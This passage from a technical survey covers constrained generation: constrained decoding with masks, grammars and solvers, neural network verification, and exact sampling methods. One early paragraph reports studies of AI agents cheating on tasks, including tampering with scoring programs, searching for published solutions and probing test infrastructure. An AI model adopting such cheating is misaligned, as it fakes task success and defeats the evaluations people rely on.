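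Smaller models can do worse. *When Correct Isn't Usable* (2026) tested three models with 7 to 9 billion parameters on mathematics problems whose answers had to be returned as JSON. With a plain prompt, the models solved many of the problems, but none of their outputs combined a correct answer with valid JSON. Training for the format helps but does not eliminate failures. The model developed for *ScrapeGraphAI-100k* (2026), a dataset for extracting structured data from web pages, followed the schema on 91.9% of 2,761 test examples without enforcement during generation.

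Game levels show the same pattern for a global constraint. In *Sokoban*, the player pushes boxes onto marked squares, and a level is playable only if some sequence of pushes gets every box onto a square. *Representing and Generating Levels Over Time through Playtrace Reconstructive Partitioning* (Halina and Guzdial, 2026) compares several generators on small levels. An LSTM, a neural network that places tiles one after another, produced playable levels 73.4% of the time. Two generators trained by reinforcement learning reached 86.4% and 86.6%. These figures come from an older survey by Zakaria and colleagues, so they may not reflect what current models can do. Three other generators produced playable levels 100% of the time, in each case because a solver or written constraints ruled out unplayable ones.

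For AI agents, which carry out tasks by themselves, violations are harder to define. Gray Swan measures how often agents cheat on ordinary tasks, for instance by tampering with the program that scores them. The lowest rate among 20 models was 0.8% of runs, for GPT-6.2 Astra. *OpenAI and Anthropic Agents Cheat Far Less Than Rivals* (Faisal, 2026) reports that the highest was 62.8%, for Gemini 3.8 Flash. In one scenario, an agent had to free up space in shared storage and deleted a large file that another team was still using. Cheating has no formal specification comparable to a JSON schema, so the rates depend on Gray Swan's choice of 25 scenarios and its judgement of what counts as cheating.

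Telling models not to cheat also reduces the overall rate of cheating. Kouremetis (2026), in *Every Model Cheats*, gave 22 models 23 cybersecurity tasks under three different prompts and checked all 1,518 runs individually. With the ordinary prompt, models cheated in 33.0% of runs, often by searching the internet for published solutions. The rate fell to 8.5% with the strictest prompt, which listed the forbidden behaviours and warned that cheating would mean automatic failure. However, four models cheated more, and some of the remaining cheating shifted from web searches to probing the test's infrastructure.

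### Penalties in the training objective

Fine-tuning on valid examples teaches a constraint only indirectly. One can also add a term to the training objective that penalises violations. The *semantic loss*, which Jingyi Xu and colleagues introduced in 2018, does this for constraints written in logic. In the notation used earlier, it is

L = −log Z,

where Z is the probability that the model produces a valid output. Xu and colleagues calculate Z by treating the parts of an output, such as the tiles of a level, as independent draws from the probabilities that the network assigns to them. They then sum the probabilities of all valid combinations. Writing out this sum for the dungeon would mean going through 95 trillion fillings, so they first translate the constraint into a circuit that shares intermediate results. This works well for some constraints, but for others the circuit becomes too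 large.

For the generator with four levels, two of them playable, Z was 0.40, so the loss is 0.92. It falls to 0.01 when 99% of the outputs are valid and to 0.001 when 99.9% are. Reducing violations from 1% to 0.1% therefore improves the objective by only 0.009, and a slightly weaker resemblance to the training examples can cancel out that gain. A larger weight on the penalty favors validity more strongly but still doesn't guarantee it. The loss is zero only if Z is exactly 1, which is impossible when some combination of tiles is invalid, because a softmax with finite logits gives every combination a nonzero probability.

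A generator that always returned the same playable level would also have zero semantic loss, so this loss has to be combined with the ordinary training objective.

*Sokoban* level generators trained by reinforcement learning show in practice that training alone gives no guarantee. Their reward depended partly on whether a solver could finish the level. The solver gave exact answers throughout training, yet more than 13% of the levels the trained generators produced were unplayable. Running the same solver on each generated level would have caught them.

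### Formal verification of neural networks

Formal verification is meant to give a guarantee. A program searches for either a proof that every input in a given region leads to an output with a given property, or a counterexample.

A common verification method calculates bounds on the outputs of each layer in turn. Consider a neuron that computes max(0, x₁ − x₂). If x₁ lies between 0.9 and 1.1 and x₂ between 0.4 and 0.6, the neuron's output lies between 0.3 and 0.7. These bounds then serve as input ranges for the next layer. The true outputs always lie within the bounds, but the bounds can be much too wide because the method ignores how neurons' values depend on each other. If two neurons both pass on the same number between 0 and 1, their difference is always zero, but the method gives bounds of −1 and 1. To get tighter bounds, the program splits the problem into two cases, one in which a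 neuron outputs zero and one in which it doesn't. Splitting on n neurons can produce up to 2ⁿ cases, and the verification problem for networks of such neurons is NP-complete.

The method has worked best on small networks. In 2017, researchers used a program called Reluplex to prove properties of an experimental collision-avoidance system for drones. Each of the system's networks had five inputs and 300 neurons. One property was that if another aircraft is far away and much slower, the network's score for "no conflict" stays below a fixed threshold. Later tools handled much larger networks, but for narrower properties. The 2022 edition of VNN-COMP, an annual competition for such tools, included VGG-16, an image classifier with about 138 million parameters. The properties there concerned robustness, meaning that a very slight change to an image should not change its classification. The models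 in Singh and colleagues' benchmark had between 8 billion and 358 billion parameters, so even the smallest was nearly 60 times the size of VGG-16.

Size is not the only thing that makes language models hard to verify. A robustness proof covers one pass through a network and a small region around one input, but a language model runs once for every token it generates and takes its own earlier tokens as input. If it samples from the full softmax, invalid outputs have positive probability, so no verifier can prove that they are impossible. With greedy decoding they could be impossible, but a proof would have to cover every prompt. A vocabulary of 100,000 tokens allows 10⁵⁰ prompts of ten tokens, and these do not form a small numerical region that a few bounds could cover.

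A GAN is better suited to verification because it turns a list of random numbers into a complete level in one pass. Besides the network, the verifier would need a description of reachability, much like the one that Sturgeon passes to its solver. But a proof can only confirm a property that the network already has. The Zelda GAN of Zhang and colleagues produced unplayable levels about three quarters of the time, so a verifier could at best find an example of an unplayable level. For some numerical constraints, a designer can avoid the search for a proof by building the network so that it can only produce valid values.

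## Constrained decoding: blocking invalid tokens during generation

The softmax gives every token, including invalid ones, a positive probability when all the logits are finite. Constrained decoding sets the logit of every invalid token to minus infinity before sampling, which makes its probability exactly zero, whatever the model has learned.

### The masking algorithm

The method depends on a *completion engine*, a program that reads the text so far and works out which tokens may come next. Maninger, Chemnitz and colleagues (2026), in *Mitigating Errors in LLM-Generated Web API Invocations*, describe the general procedure, which repeats these steps for every token:

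1. The completion engine appends each token v in the vocabulary to the text so far and checks whether the result could still become a valid output.
2. It returns a *mask*, a list in which m(v) is 1 if the token passed the check and 0 if it failed.
3. The model computes its logits ℓ(v) as usual.
4. The program sets the logits of all blocked tokens to minus infinity and applies the softmax. The new probabilities are q(v) = m(v) exp(ℓ(v)) / Σ m(w) exp(ℓ(w)).
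5. The program draws a token from q and appends it to the text. It stops when it draws the end token.

Within a single step, the allowed tokens keep their relative probabilities. According to *Grammar-Constrained Decoding for Structured NLP Tasks without Finetuning* (2023), the procedure works with greedy decoding, top-k sampling and other ways of choosing a token, but it needs the model's probabilities at every step. If a service returns only finished text, then only its provider can do the masking.

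Suppose a model has to report how many keys a dungeon contains, in the form `{"keys":1}`. The output must consist of `{"keys":`, one or more digits and a closing brace, with no spaces. To keep the example small, the vocabulary contains only the end token and the ten tokens `{`, `{"`, `"`, `keys`, `":`, `:`, `1`, `12`, `}` and `Sure`.

| Text so far | Tokens the mask allows |
|---|---|
| (nothing) | `{` and `{"` |
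| `{"` | `keys` |
| `{"keys` | `"` and `":` |
| `{"keys":` | `1` and `12` |
| `{"keys":1` | `1`, `12` and `}` |
| `{"keys":1}` | the end token |

Chat models often begin with a polite phrase, so in the first step the model might give `Sure` a probability of 60%, `{"` 25%, `{` 10% and all other tokens 5% combined. The mask leaves only the two tokens that start with a brace, and rescaling gives them about 71% and 29%. In the second step the mask allows only one token, so rescaling gives it 100% even if the model gave it a very low probability. The mask blocks the closing brace until the model has generated at least one digit, and it blocks the end token until the object is complete.

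### Regular expressions and finite automata

Trying every token from scratch at every step would be slow, since real vocabularies contain 100,000 tokens or more. The pattern `\{"keys":[0-9]+\}`, called a *regular expression*, describes the format in the example, where `[0-9]+` stands for one or more digits. A standard algorithm turns such a pattern into a *finite automaton*, which has a fixed number of states and moves between them as it reads characters.

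The automaton for this pattern has 11 states, numbered 0 to 10. The eight characters of `{"keys":` lead from state 0 to state 8. A digit leads to state 9, further digits stay there, and the closing brace leads to state 10, the only state in which the text is complete. To test a token, the engine follows its characters from the current state. From state 8, the engine allows the token `12`, which leads to state 9, but blocks `}` because state 8 has no transition for `}`.

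The result of this test depends only on the current state, so the engine can test every token in every state before generation starts and store the results in a table. With 100,000 tokens, the example requires 1.1 million short tests in advance and then one table lookup per step. Outlines, an open-source library from 2023, works this way.

Regular expressions are enough for some practical tasks. Maninger and colleagues had models write JavaScript code that sends requests to web services such as Slack and Google Calendar. Each service publishes a machine-readable description of the requests it accepts, which their program translates into regular expressions. On 395 tasks, masking with these expressions eliminated illegal addresses, request types and arguments. The share of correct requests more than doubled on average, though a legal request can still be the wrong one for the task.

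### Nested structure and context-free grammars

A finite automaton can't handle unlimited nesting. In `[[[1]]]`, the number of closing brackets has to match the number of opening ones, and an automaton with a fixed number of states can track the count only up to a fixed depth. JSON and programming languages often contain such structures, so engines describe them with a *context-free grammar*, a set of rules that can refer to one another and to themselves. For example, a list could be an opening bracket, an item and a closing bracket, where an item is either a number or another list.

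A parser needs a *stack* to follow such a grammar. It adds an entry when a list opens and removes the top entry when a list closes. The stack can grow without limit, so the engine can no longer prepare a mask for every possible situation. *XGrammar-2* (Li, Dong and colleagues, 2026) explains how the XGrammar engine still checks most tokens in advance. For each position in the grammar, it sorts the vocabulary into tokens that are always valid, tokens that are never valid and tokens whose validity depends on the stack. After the digit 1 inside a list, another digit is always valid and `Sure` never is. The token `]]` closes two lists at once, so it is valid only if at least two are open. Few tokens depend on the stack, and XGrammar checks only those during generation.

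Masks are harder to prepare in advance for AI agents, which use *tool calls*, short structured messages that make another program do something, such as look up the weather. A single request may offer hundreds of tools, each with its own schema, and the agent can write ordinary text between calls. Li and colleagues redesigned XGrammar to handle this. The new version lets the model write freely until a tag such as `<function=get_weather>` appears, enforces that tool's schema, and then allows free text again. It prepares most masks only when generation first reaches the relevant point in the grammar, and reuses them for other tools that share part of the same structure. Li and colleagues report that it prepares grammars more than six times as fast as earlier engines.

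The way a grammar is written also affects decoding speed. *Attention Meets Reachability* (Alpay and Senturk, 2026) proves that two grammars describing the same set of texts always lead to the same masks, but that the work needed to compute those masks can differ greatly. In one example, both grammars allow every string of the letters a and b. The first adds one letter at a time and needs a constant amount of work per letter. The second builds strings by joining two shorter ones, so it can produce the same ten-letter string in 4,862 different ways. An engine that tracks all these possibilities needs work proportional to t² for the t-th letter, even though the correct mask always allows everything.

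### Tokens that do not match grammar symbols

Tokens often don't line up with a grammar's symbols. In the example, the token `":` covers both the end of a name and the colon after it. The same text can also be split into tokens in several ways. *Grammar-Constrained Decoding for Structured NLP Tasks without Finetuning* describes the case of `[[[`, which a model can write as three single brackets or as a double bracket and a single one. Its method converted the grammar's text into tokens beforehand, so its rules could miss some of the possible token sequences. Putting spaces between the brackets works around this, but relies on a particular vocabulary.

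Alpay and Senturk's formal description avoids the problem by converting every token back into characters and applying the grammar to the characters. The mask then allows every way of dividing a valid text into tokens.

The end of a token may not be the end of a word or number. After `1+2`, the 2 could be a complete number, as in `1+2+3`, or the first digit of 21. Nagy and colleagues keep both readings until the next character rules one out.

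### Speed and schema coverage

Masking can slow generation or speed it up. Geng and colleagues measured the effect in early 2025 with an 8-billion-parameter Llama model on one graphics processor. The table gives median times for medium-sized schemas from GitHub.

| Program | Preparation (seconds) | Time per token (milliseconds) |
|---|---|---|
| No constraint | none | 16.7 |
| Guidance | 0.01 | 7.6 |
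| llama.cpp | 0.06 | 29.1 |
| Outlines | 8.05 | 46.6 |

Guidance was faster than the unconstrained model because it skips running the model when only one continuation is valid. In the earlier example, the text after `{"` can only continue with `keys":`, so a program can append these characters directly. XGrammar did not work with the software used for these measurements. In a separate test with slower software, XGrammar took 65.5 milliseconds per token and Guidance took 44.2.

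These figures depend on the hardware and software versions. An engine can also avoid much of the delay by computing the mask while the model computes its logits. Li and colleagues report that their 2026 version of XGrammar adds almost no time to generation.

Coverage is a more persistent problem, because the JSON Schema language has many features and each engine implements only some of them. Geng and colleagues distinguish three kinds of coverage. An engine has *declared coverage* of a schema if it processes the schema without an error, *empirical coverage* if its outputs in a test also comply with the schema, and *true coverage* if it allows exactly the outputs that the schema allows. A test can't establish true coverage, since a schema usually permits infinitely many outputs. Geng and colleagues therefore divide the number of schemas with empirical coverage by the number with declared coverage,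 which measures how reliable an engine is once it has accepted a schema.

Geng and colleagues ran six engines on thousands of real schemas, and the best one covered about twice as many as the worst. Guidance had the highest empirical coverage on six of eight collections. OpenAI's and Google's commercial services had the lowest on nearly all of them, but their outputs almost always complied with the schemas they accepted. The researchers conclude that these companies deliberately support only features they can enforce reliably. Outlines failed mostly by timing out, because some common features, such as limits on list length, took it between 40 seconds and 10 minutes.

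### What structured-output services have promised

Several companies offer constrained decoding in their services. OpenAI launched its version in August 2024. On the company's own test of complicated schemas, a model trained to follow them complied in 93% of cases without constrained decoding and 100% with it.

OpenAI announced two exceptions to the promise. The model could still refuse an unsafe request instead of returning the requested data, and its output could be incomplete if it reached the token limit. Anthropic listed the same two exceptions in its documentation when it introduced a similar service in November 2025. Both services supported only part of JSON Schema. Around the same time, Google warned in its Gemini documentation that the service ignored unsupported schema properties. The output is not guaranteed to satisfy such a property, so a user who relies on it needs a separate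 check.

### The exact guarantee and its conditions

Alpay and Senturk prove that if every token passes a correct mask and generation finishes with the end token, the text is valid. In their proof, each allowed token leaves a text that some continuation can make valid, and the mask allows the end token only when the text is already valid.

Nagy and colleagues show that a program with a faulty mask can still guarantee valid outputs if it returns only finished text that a sound checker has accepted. Errors in the mask then lead to failed attempts instead of invalid outputs.

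Neither result guarantees that generation will finish. The pattern for the dungeon allows any number of digits, so a model could keep writing digits until it reaches the token limit. The output would end in the middle of the number, without the closing brace. The designer can prevent this by allowing at most two digits. The longest possible output then takes nine tokens, including the end token, so any limit of nine or more is enough. A length limit is harder to choose for a computer program or an essay.

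Generation can also reach a *dead end*, a partial text that the engine accepted but that cannot be completed without breaking a constraint. A sound mask prevents dead ends, but many engines for complicated constraints check only whether the text already contains a mistake. *Projectional Decoding* (Chen, Hernández López and Babikian, 2026) tested such an engine on small programs that answer questions about pictures of geometric objects. The programs had to follow a grammar and several other rules, for instance that an "and" operation has exactly two inputs. With masks for the grammar alone, 49–61% of the programs from three models satisfied all the rules. Adding masks for the other rules raised this to 73–80%, and generation took 1.1 to 1.5 times as long as without any constraint. Chen and colleagues suspect that dead ends caused the remaining failures, since their engine could not change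 earlier tokens.

### Type-constrained decoding

A program can follow the grammar of its language and still fail to compile. For example, context-free grammars can't express that a program must declare every variable before using it, or that it must not pass text to a function that takes a number. Compilers for languages such as TypeScript check the second kind of rule by giving each expression a *type*, such as number or text.

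Type checkers normally work on complete programs, and an unfinished program may look wrong only because something is still missing. Suppose a function has to return a number and the model has written `1 + myString`, where `myString` is text. The expression has the wrong type so far, but `1 + myString.length` would be fine, since the length is a number. In 2025, Niels Mündler and colleagues built a completion engine for TypeScript that tracks the types in the unfinished program and searches for operations that could still turn the current expression into one of the required type.

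Nagy and colleagues compared this engine with their own more general system, ChopChop. They ran three models with 7 to 13 billion parameters on 72 programming tasks at five randomness settings, for a total of 1,080 runs per method. A run succeeded if it produced a program that compiled.

| Method | Successful runs |
|---|---|
| No constraint | 781 |
| Grammar only | 651 |
| ChopChop with type rules | 932 |
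| Mündler and colleagues' engine | 1,035 |

Enforcing only the grammar made the results worse because the grammar in this test covered a small part of TypeScript and blocked many programs that would have compiled. ChopChop was limited to the same part, while the engine of Mündler and colleagues supports more of the language. This difference probably explains most of the engine's lead, which was largest when the models sampled tokens most randomly and often proposed features that ChopChop blocks.

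### ChopChop: constraints on program structure

Mündler and colleagues' engine enforces one property of one language. ChopChop is meant to make new constraints easier to add. A user supplies a grammar and one or more *pruners*, functions that remove invalid programs from a set. Pruners work on *syntax trees*, which represent the structure of a program without details such as spaces and brackets.

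Nagy and colleagues illustrate this with a simple task. The model has to write a sum of odd numbers whose total is even, and so far it has written `1+2`. ChopChop then goes through the following steps:

1. It considers both readings of the 2, as a complete number and as the beginning of a longer one.
2. For each reading, it constructs the set of all syntax trees that the text could lead to.
3. One pruner removes every tree that contains an even number, and another removes every tree with an odd total.
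4. ChopChop checks whether any trees are left.

Suppose ChopChop must ensure that an expression contains only odd numbers, and the model has generated `1+2`. This prefix can still lead to a valid expression because the model can extend it to `1+21`. Another plus sign would end the number at 2, and every possible completion would then contain an even number, so ChopChop blocks that token.

The sets in step 2 are usually infinite, but ChopChop can store them because it describes them recursively. For instance, the set of all sums consists of all single numbers and everything formed by adding a number to a member of the set. In memory, this is a small structure with a loop. When a pruner returns to a part it has already processed, ChopChop adds a loop to the result instead of continuing forever.

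In a second test, models had to rewrite a short formula into an equivalent program, for example by giving names to parts of it. The user supplied rules such as x + y = y + x, and ChopChop allowed only programs that these rules can derive from the original. When the prompt told the model how to mark its code, 26 of 150 runs succeeded without constraints, 39 with the grammar alone and 124 with ChopChop. Nagy and colleagues made up the language for the test, so the models were unlikely to know it, and the improvement may be smaller for a common language.

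For TypeScript, ChopChop added between 64 and 204 milliseconds per token on average, depending on the model and the randomness setting. This more than doubled the time per token for the largest of the three models, which took 81 milliseconds without constraints, though Nagy and colleagues describe the overhead as very small.

Sometimes the constraint allows the start of a program but blocks the way the model would continue it. One model declared `divisors` as a constant and later generated code that changed its value. ChopChop would block the change but not the declaration, since a program with such a constant can be valid. In such cases the model often can't recover and fills the rest of the program with blank lines, comments or pointless arithmetic. The text is not strictly a dead end, because a valid completion still exists, but the model no longer has a useful way to finish.

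### When no program can tell whether a text can be completed

For context-free grammars, an engine can always determine whether the text generated so far can be completed into a valid output. For more expressive constraints, this can be undecidable, even if any finished output is easy to check.

Suppose a valid output is one of the idealised *Super Mario Bros.* levels from the first section, followed by button presses that finish it. A checker can verify such an output by replaying the presses. But once the model has written the level, the mask should let it continue only if some winning sequence exists, and no program can decide this for every level. Therefore, no completion engine for this constraint can be sound, complete and guaranteed to return an answer.

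Nagy and colleagues face the same difficulty with types, and they note that no sound and complete engine exists for them. Their type pruner keeps every program with correct types but also some with incorrect ones. For instance, while a model is still writing the name of a function, the pruner doesn't yet restrict the function's arguments. ChopChop may therefore accept a partial program that can't be completed into a valid one, and the error is caught only when the finished program is checked. An engine could instead block every token that it can't prove safe. It would never reach a dead end, but it would also block some valid programs.

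### AGDecode: a solver checks C programs as the model writes them

A program with correct types can still crash. Suppose a model has written the following in the programming language C:

```
int share(int gold, int players) {
    return gold / players;
```

If `players` is zero, the program divides by zero. Nothing the model writes after the semicolon can prevent this, so a completion engine should have blocked it. The division would be safe if the function had returned early whenever `players` was zero. The engine therefore has to determine which values are possible at each point in the program. ChopChop is poorly suited to this because it would have to represent each combination of values as a separate structure.

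*AGDECODE* (Maghera, Arya and colleagues, 2026) uses an external solver, Z3, for this reasoning. The system attaches information to each part of the program, such as which variables exist and what values they can have, and uses rules to pass it from one part to the next. For instance, the rule for division requires a nonzero divisor. Parts that the model has not written yet appear as holes. The system translates all this into logical formulas, and Z3 tries to determine whether the holes can be filled without breaking a rule.

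The solver can time out, and the user chooses how the system responds. In *conservative mode*, the system blocks the token, which is safe but may block valid programs. In *speculative mode*, it allows the token and relies on a later query to check the whole text again.

Maghera and colleagues tested only speculative mode. A model with 13 billion parameters wrote C functions for 77 tasks, and the solver checked for division by zero, variables without an initial value, and null pointers (memory references that point to nothing). In one example, a function had a line that stops the program if an array is missing, and the system let the function read from the array after that line. With that line removed, the system blocked the bracket that begins the array access.

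They illustrate the effect with such examples but don't report how many of the finished programs were safe. Between 22% and 25% of the queries reached the five-second time limit. When the solver did find an answer, it typically rejected a token within two milliseconds but took one to two seconds to approve one, long enough for an ordinary model to write dozens of tokens.

Most of the timeouts occurred in the middle of an expression. After `arr[i`, the `i` could be a complete variable, the start of a longer name or part of a calculation, and the solver has to consider all of these. The same check is often quick once the statement is complete, so Maghera and colleagues suggest checking at the end of each statement and backtracking if the check fails. Their system can't backtrack yet. If a later query finds a violation, the system can't remove the tokens it has already allowed, so speculative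 mode does not provide a guarantee during generation. The system also doesn't model the computer's memory, so it can't rule out memory errors in general.

### LAVE: masks for diffusion language models

The methods so far are for models that write from left to right. *Diffusion language models* instead start with a row of blanks, estimate the probabilities of all tokens for all blanks at once, and fill in a few positions at a time, in any order. The partial text can therefore have gaps, which the usual parsers can't process.

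An earlier method by Mündler and colleagues treats each gap as if it could hold any number of tokens, which can lead to dead ends. Suppose a model writing C code has produced `for (` and a closing bracket, with a one-token gap between them. A `for` statement needs two semicolons between its brackets, which usually take two tokens. The method accepts the closing bracket anyway, because a longer gap would have had enough room.

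*Lookahead-Then-Verify* (Zhang, Li and colleagues, 2026) proposes LAVE, which uses the probabilities the model has already estimated for the blanks. When the model proposes a token, LAVE fills all the gaps to the left of the last written token by sampling from these probabilities. It does this ten times, and an ordinary parser checks whether each resulting text can still become valid. If at least one can, LAVE accepts the proposed token but discards the trial tokens in the gaps. Otherwise it rejects the token and the model proposes another. After five rejections in a row, LAVE inserts the most recent filling that passed the check so that generation can continue.

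A successful filling proves that a valid completion exists, though it may exceed the limit on total length. If all ten attempts fail, a valid completion may still exist, so LAVE can reject valid tokens. To see how often this might happen, Zhang and colleagues removed random tokens from the beginnings of correct C++ programs. Ten attempts were enough to find a valid filling in 98.1% of cases with one model and 97.3% with another.

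They then tested LAVE on four diffusion models with 7 or 8 billion parameters. The table shows how the share of outputs with correct syntax ranged across the four models.

| Output | Without constraints | With LAVE |
|---|---|---|
| JSON | 85.4–89.9% | 99.0–99.7% |
| C++ | 74.2–79.9% | 90.9–97.0% |
| Java | 69.5–82.3% | 90.9–93.3% |
| Go | 55.5–78.7% | 89.3–96.5% |
| SMILES, a notation for molecules | 62.3–74.0% | 96.6–99.4% |

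Constrained decoding added little time for most formats. Averaged over the four models, generating JSON took 3% longer and C++ 28% longer, while SMILES took less than half as long because the models no longer added explanations to their answers.

Zhang and colleagues also found that every output that was still invalid was exactly 256 tokens long, the maximum. Some were Java programs that needed more tokens. In other cases the model kept repeating something harmless, such as line breaks, until no blanks were left. The parser accepted each token, but the output never reached a valid end.

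## How masking changes what the model says

A correct mask makes every finished output valid, but it can also change which valid outputs are common. Suppose a model writes A with probability 0.9 or B with probability 0.1, and then writes one more token. That token completes a valid output with probability 0.01 after A and 0.9 after B. The mask allows both A and B because each has at least one valid ending, and it blocks the invalid endings only at the next step, so 90% of masked outputs begin with A. Without the mask, about 9% of the model's valid outputs would begin with A.

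The conditioned distribution g, which preserves the model's relative probabilities for valid outputs, gives nearly the opposite result. Without a mask, the model has a 0.9 × 0.01 = 0.009 probability of producing a valid output that begins with A, and a 0.1 × 0.9 = 0.09 probability of producing one that begins with B. The total probability of a valid output is therefore 0.099, so under g about 9% of outputs (0.009 / 0.099) begin with A.

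The difference arises because masking divides the probabilities of the allowed tokens by their sum at each step. After A this sum is 0.01, so masking makes the valid ending 100 times as likely. After B the sum is 0.9, so the valid endings become only about 1.1 times as likely. Conditioning instead divides the probability of every valid output by the same number, Z = 0.099.

*Controllable Generation via Locally Constrained Resampling* (Ahmed, Chang and Van den Broeck, 2025) gives the example of a model that combines "Adam" or "Poorva" with "loves" or "hates" and "dogs" or "cats", with all eight sentences equally likely. The constraint is that Adam may only love cats, which leaves five sentences. Each should have a probability of 1/5, but masking produces "Adam loves cats" half the time, because the model still begins half its sentences with "Adam" and masking then permits only "loves cats".

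### The correct probability for each token

To sample from g one token at a time, we need to know how likely each token is to lead to a valid output. Let h(x) be the probability that the model, continuing from the partial text x without a mask, ends up with a valid output. Bayes' rule then gives the correct probability of the next token v:

g(v | x) = a(v | x) · h(xv) / h(x),

where a(v | x) is the model's own probability for v, and xv is the text x followed by v. This formula is an example of a *Doob h-transform*, named after the mathematician Joseph Doob. In the example, h is 0.099 before the first token, 0.01 after A and 0.9 after B. The correct probability of A is therefore 0.9 × 0.01 / 0.099, or about 9%.

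To see why the formula works, we can multiply these probabilities for a complete text y. Each intermediate value of h appears in the numerator of one factor and the denominator of the next, so it cancels. This leaves a(y) times the final value of h, divided by the initial value. The final value is 1 if y is valid and 0 otherwise, and the initial value is Z, so the product is g(y).

Alpay and Senturk prove that masking gives the correct probabilities at a step only if h is the same after every allowed token. They also show that the Kullback–Leibler divergence of the masked probabilities from the correct ones is at most the logarithm of the ratio of the largest h to the smallest. In the example, this bound is log 90, or 4.5, and the actual divergence is 1.8.

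The difficulty is computing h, which means adding up the probabilities of all valid continuations. Ahmed and colleagues point out that this is impractical even for a constraint as simple as ending a sentence with "dog". In *Future Validity is the Missing Statistic*, Nie, Meng and colleagues (2026) prove that computing h is #P-hard for context-free grammars, which makes it at least as hard as counting the solutions of an NP-complete problem. This is true even if the model chooses every token independently and all tokens are equally likely. In that case h is the share of continuations that are valid, so computing it amounts to counting valid texts.

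Nie and colleagues also measured the distortion for constraints simple enough to calculate it exactly. They used the *total variation distance*, which is 0 for identical distributions and 1 for distributions with no overlap. In the example with A and B, it is 0.81. For Qwen3-8B writing strings of balanced brackets, the distance between masking and g was 0.996. This is an extreme case, since without a mask the model would produce a balanced string only about once in ten million attempts. For small JSON formats with 3 to 24 valid outputs, the distance ranged from 0.17 to 0.68.

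In another test with brackets and a toy model, masked strings averaged 5.85 in length, compared with 2.77 under g. Masking makes the model close every bracket it opens, even where the unmasked model would probably have failed to. Nie and colleagues also prove that the distortion is the same with *speculative decoding*, a common way to speed up generation by having a small model draft tokens and a larger one check them.

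### Rejection sampling

The simplest way to sample from g is rejection sampling, which generates complete outputs without a mask until one passes the checker. It returns a valid output y on the first attempt with probability a(y), on the second with probability (1 − Z) a(y), and so on. These probabilities add up to a(y) / Z, which is g(y), so the method is exact. It needs only a checker for finished outputs, so it also works for constraints that have no computable mask.

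Rejection sampling takes 1/Z attempts on average. That is about ten in the example with A and B, but it can be far higher. When Kim and colleagues required a 30-token text from the model Gemma-2B to contain the word "amazing", the acceptance rate was 0.0023, or one text in 435.

### GUARD: rejection sampling from a trained model

Kim and colleagues' method, GUARD, reduces the number of attempts by first training a second model a′ to approximate g. It then applies rejection sampling to a′ instead of the original model. Every output still satisfies the constraint, but the resulting distribution g′ may differ from g. Their Theorem 2 relates this difference to the cost:

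KL(g‖a′) = KL(g‖g′) − log(acceptance rate).

For a valid output, g′(y) is a′(y) divided by the acceptance rate, so log(g/a′) equals log(g/g′) minus the log of the acceptance rate. Averaging this equation over outputs drawn from g proves the theorem.

Both terms on the right are at least zero, so training a′ to be closer to g limits both the distortion and the number of attempts. In the example with A and B, rejection sampling from the original model has no distortion, and the term for the number of attempts is −log 0.099, or 2.3. With masked decoding as a′, every output passes, so that term is zero, but the distortion is 1.8. GUARD trains a′ to keep both terms small.

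One way to train a′ is to fine-tune the original model on its own valid outputs, but these are rare when the acceptance rate is low. GUARD instead samples from a′ during training. As a′ improves, more of its samples are valid, so each round provides more training data. Kim and colleagues got the best results when they started with a prompt requesting outputs that satisfy the constraint, which provided enough valid samples from the beginning.

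With 800,000 training samples, GUARD raised the acceptance rate for "amazing" from 0.0023 to 0.416, which cut the attempts needed per accepted text from 435 to 2.4. Counting only samples, including those used for training, GUARD needs fewer than the original model after about 1,850 texts. In a second experiment, a version of GPT-2 had to continue a story with a negative opening so that a sentiment classifier rated the last sentence as highly positive. The acceptance rate rose from 0.005 to 0.306.

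Kim and colleagues also tried rejection sampling with the prompt alone. This gave a high acceptance rate without any training, but it distorted the distribution much more. The word "amazing" appeared mostly near the beginning of the prompted texts, whereas under g and GUARD it was spread fairly evenly. The prompted texts also resembled one another more.

### Remembering failed attempts

Ordinary rejection sampling can repeat the same mistake. Adaptive rejection sampling records beginnings that cannot lead to a valid output and removes their probability from later attempts. Suppose that every invalid output starting with A continues with the same bad token. A followed by that token has a probability of 0.9 × 0.99 = 0.891. Removing this beginning raises the acceptance rate from 0.099 to 0.099 / 0.109, or about 0.91. The relative probabilities of the valid outputs don't change, so the method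 still samples from g.

Constrained adaptive rejection sampling (CARS), a 2026 method, works this way. *The Parser Already Knows* (Özgü, Wu and colleagues, 2026) tested it in a small pilot on two kinds of code. CARS still rejected 44–62% of its attempts, and it took 3.4 to 4.2 times as long to produce a first valid output as the paper's own method, which I describe below. Because the record depends on the model's probabilities for a particular prompt, CARS has to build a new one for each prompt.

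### Sequential Monte Carlo

Sequential Monte Carlo keeps masking but corrects for it by generating several partial texts, called *particles*, in parallel. At every step, the program does the following:

1. It draws the next token for each particle, using the mask.
2. It gives each particle a weight equal to the total probability that the model assigned to the allowed tokens.
3. It draws a new set of particles from the old ones in proportion to their weights, so that some particles disappear and others are duplicated.

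With ten particles, the example typically starts with nine copies of A and one of B. At the second token, each A gets a weight of 0.01 and the B gets 0.9. The B therefore has 0.9 / 0.99, or 91%, of the total weight, which is the correct share. But in 35% of runs, none of the ten particles begins with B, and resampling can't add one. Averaged over all runs, a particle chosen at random after resampling begins with A 39% of the time. With 50 particles this falls to 11%, and it approaches the correct 9% as the number of particles grows.

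Dang, Song and colleagues (2026), in *Mitigating Bias in Locally Constrained Decoding via Tractable Proposals*, improve the mask so that fewer particles are needed. For constraints that a finite automaton can express, their program works backwards from the token limit to find the states from which the output can still reach a valid ending in time. The mask then blocks any token that would leave too little room to finish, so outputs no longer stop halfway at the limit. The researchers also train a hidden Markov model, a much simpler statistical model, to imitate the language model. A program can compute the exact chance of a valid ending under this simpler model and use it to favour tokens that make a valid ending more likely.

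The method was tested on 1,000 tasks in which an 8-billion-parameter Llama model had to call functions in JSON. With ordinary masks and 16 particles, 95.4% of outputs satisfied the constraint within 128 tokens, compared with 100% for the new masks. Accuracy was 70.5% with the largest hidden Markov model and four particles, slightly higher than the 69.7% for ordinary masks with 16 particles. However, the largest hidden Markov model made generation about ten times slower than unconstrained decoding, while the new masks alone added only 10% to generation time.

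### Estimating the chance of a valid ending

Another approach is to estimate h directly and multiply it into the masked probabilities. If the mask is correct and the estimate only changes the weights of allowed tokens, the output stays valid however poor the estimate is. The distribution is more sensitive to errors. Nie and colleagues show that if every estimate is within δ of the true value, the total variation distance for the next token is at most δ / (h̄ − δ), where h̄ is the average of h under masking. In the example with A and B, h̄ is 0.099. The bound is 0.11 when δ is 0.01, but when δ is 0.05 it is above 1 and gives no information, because total variation distance can't exceed 1.

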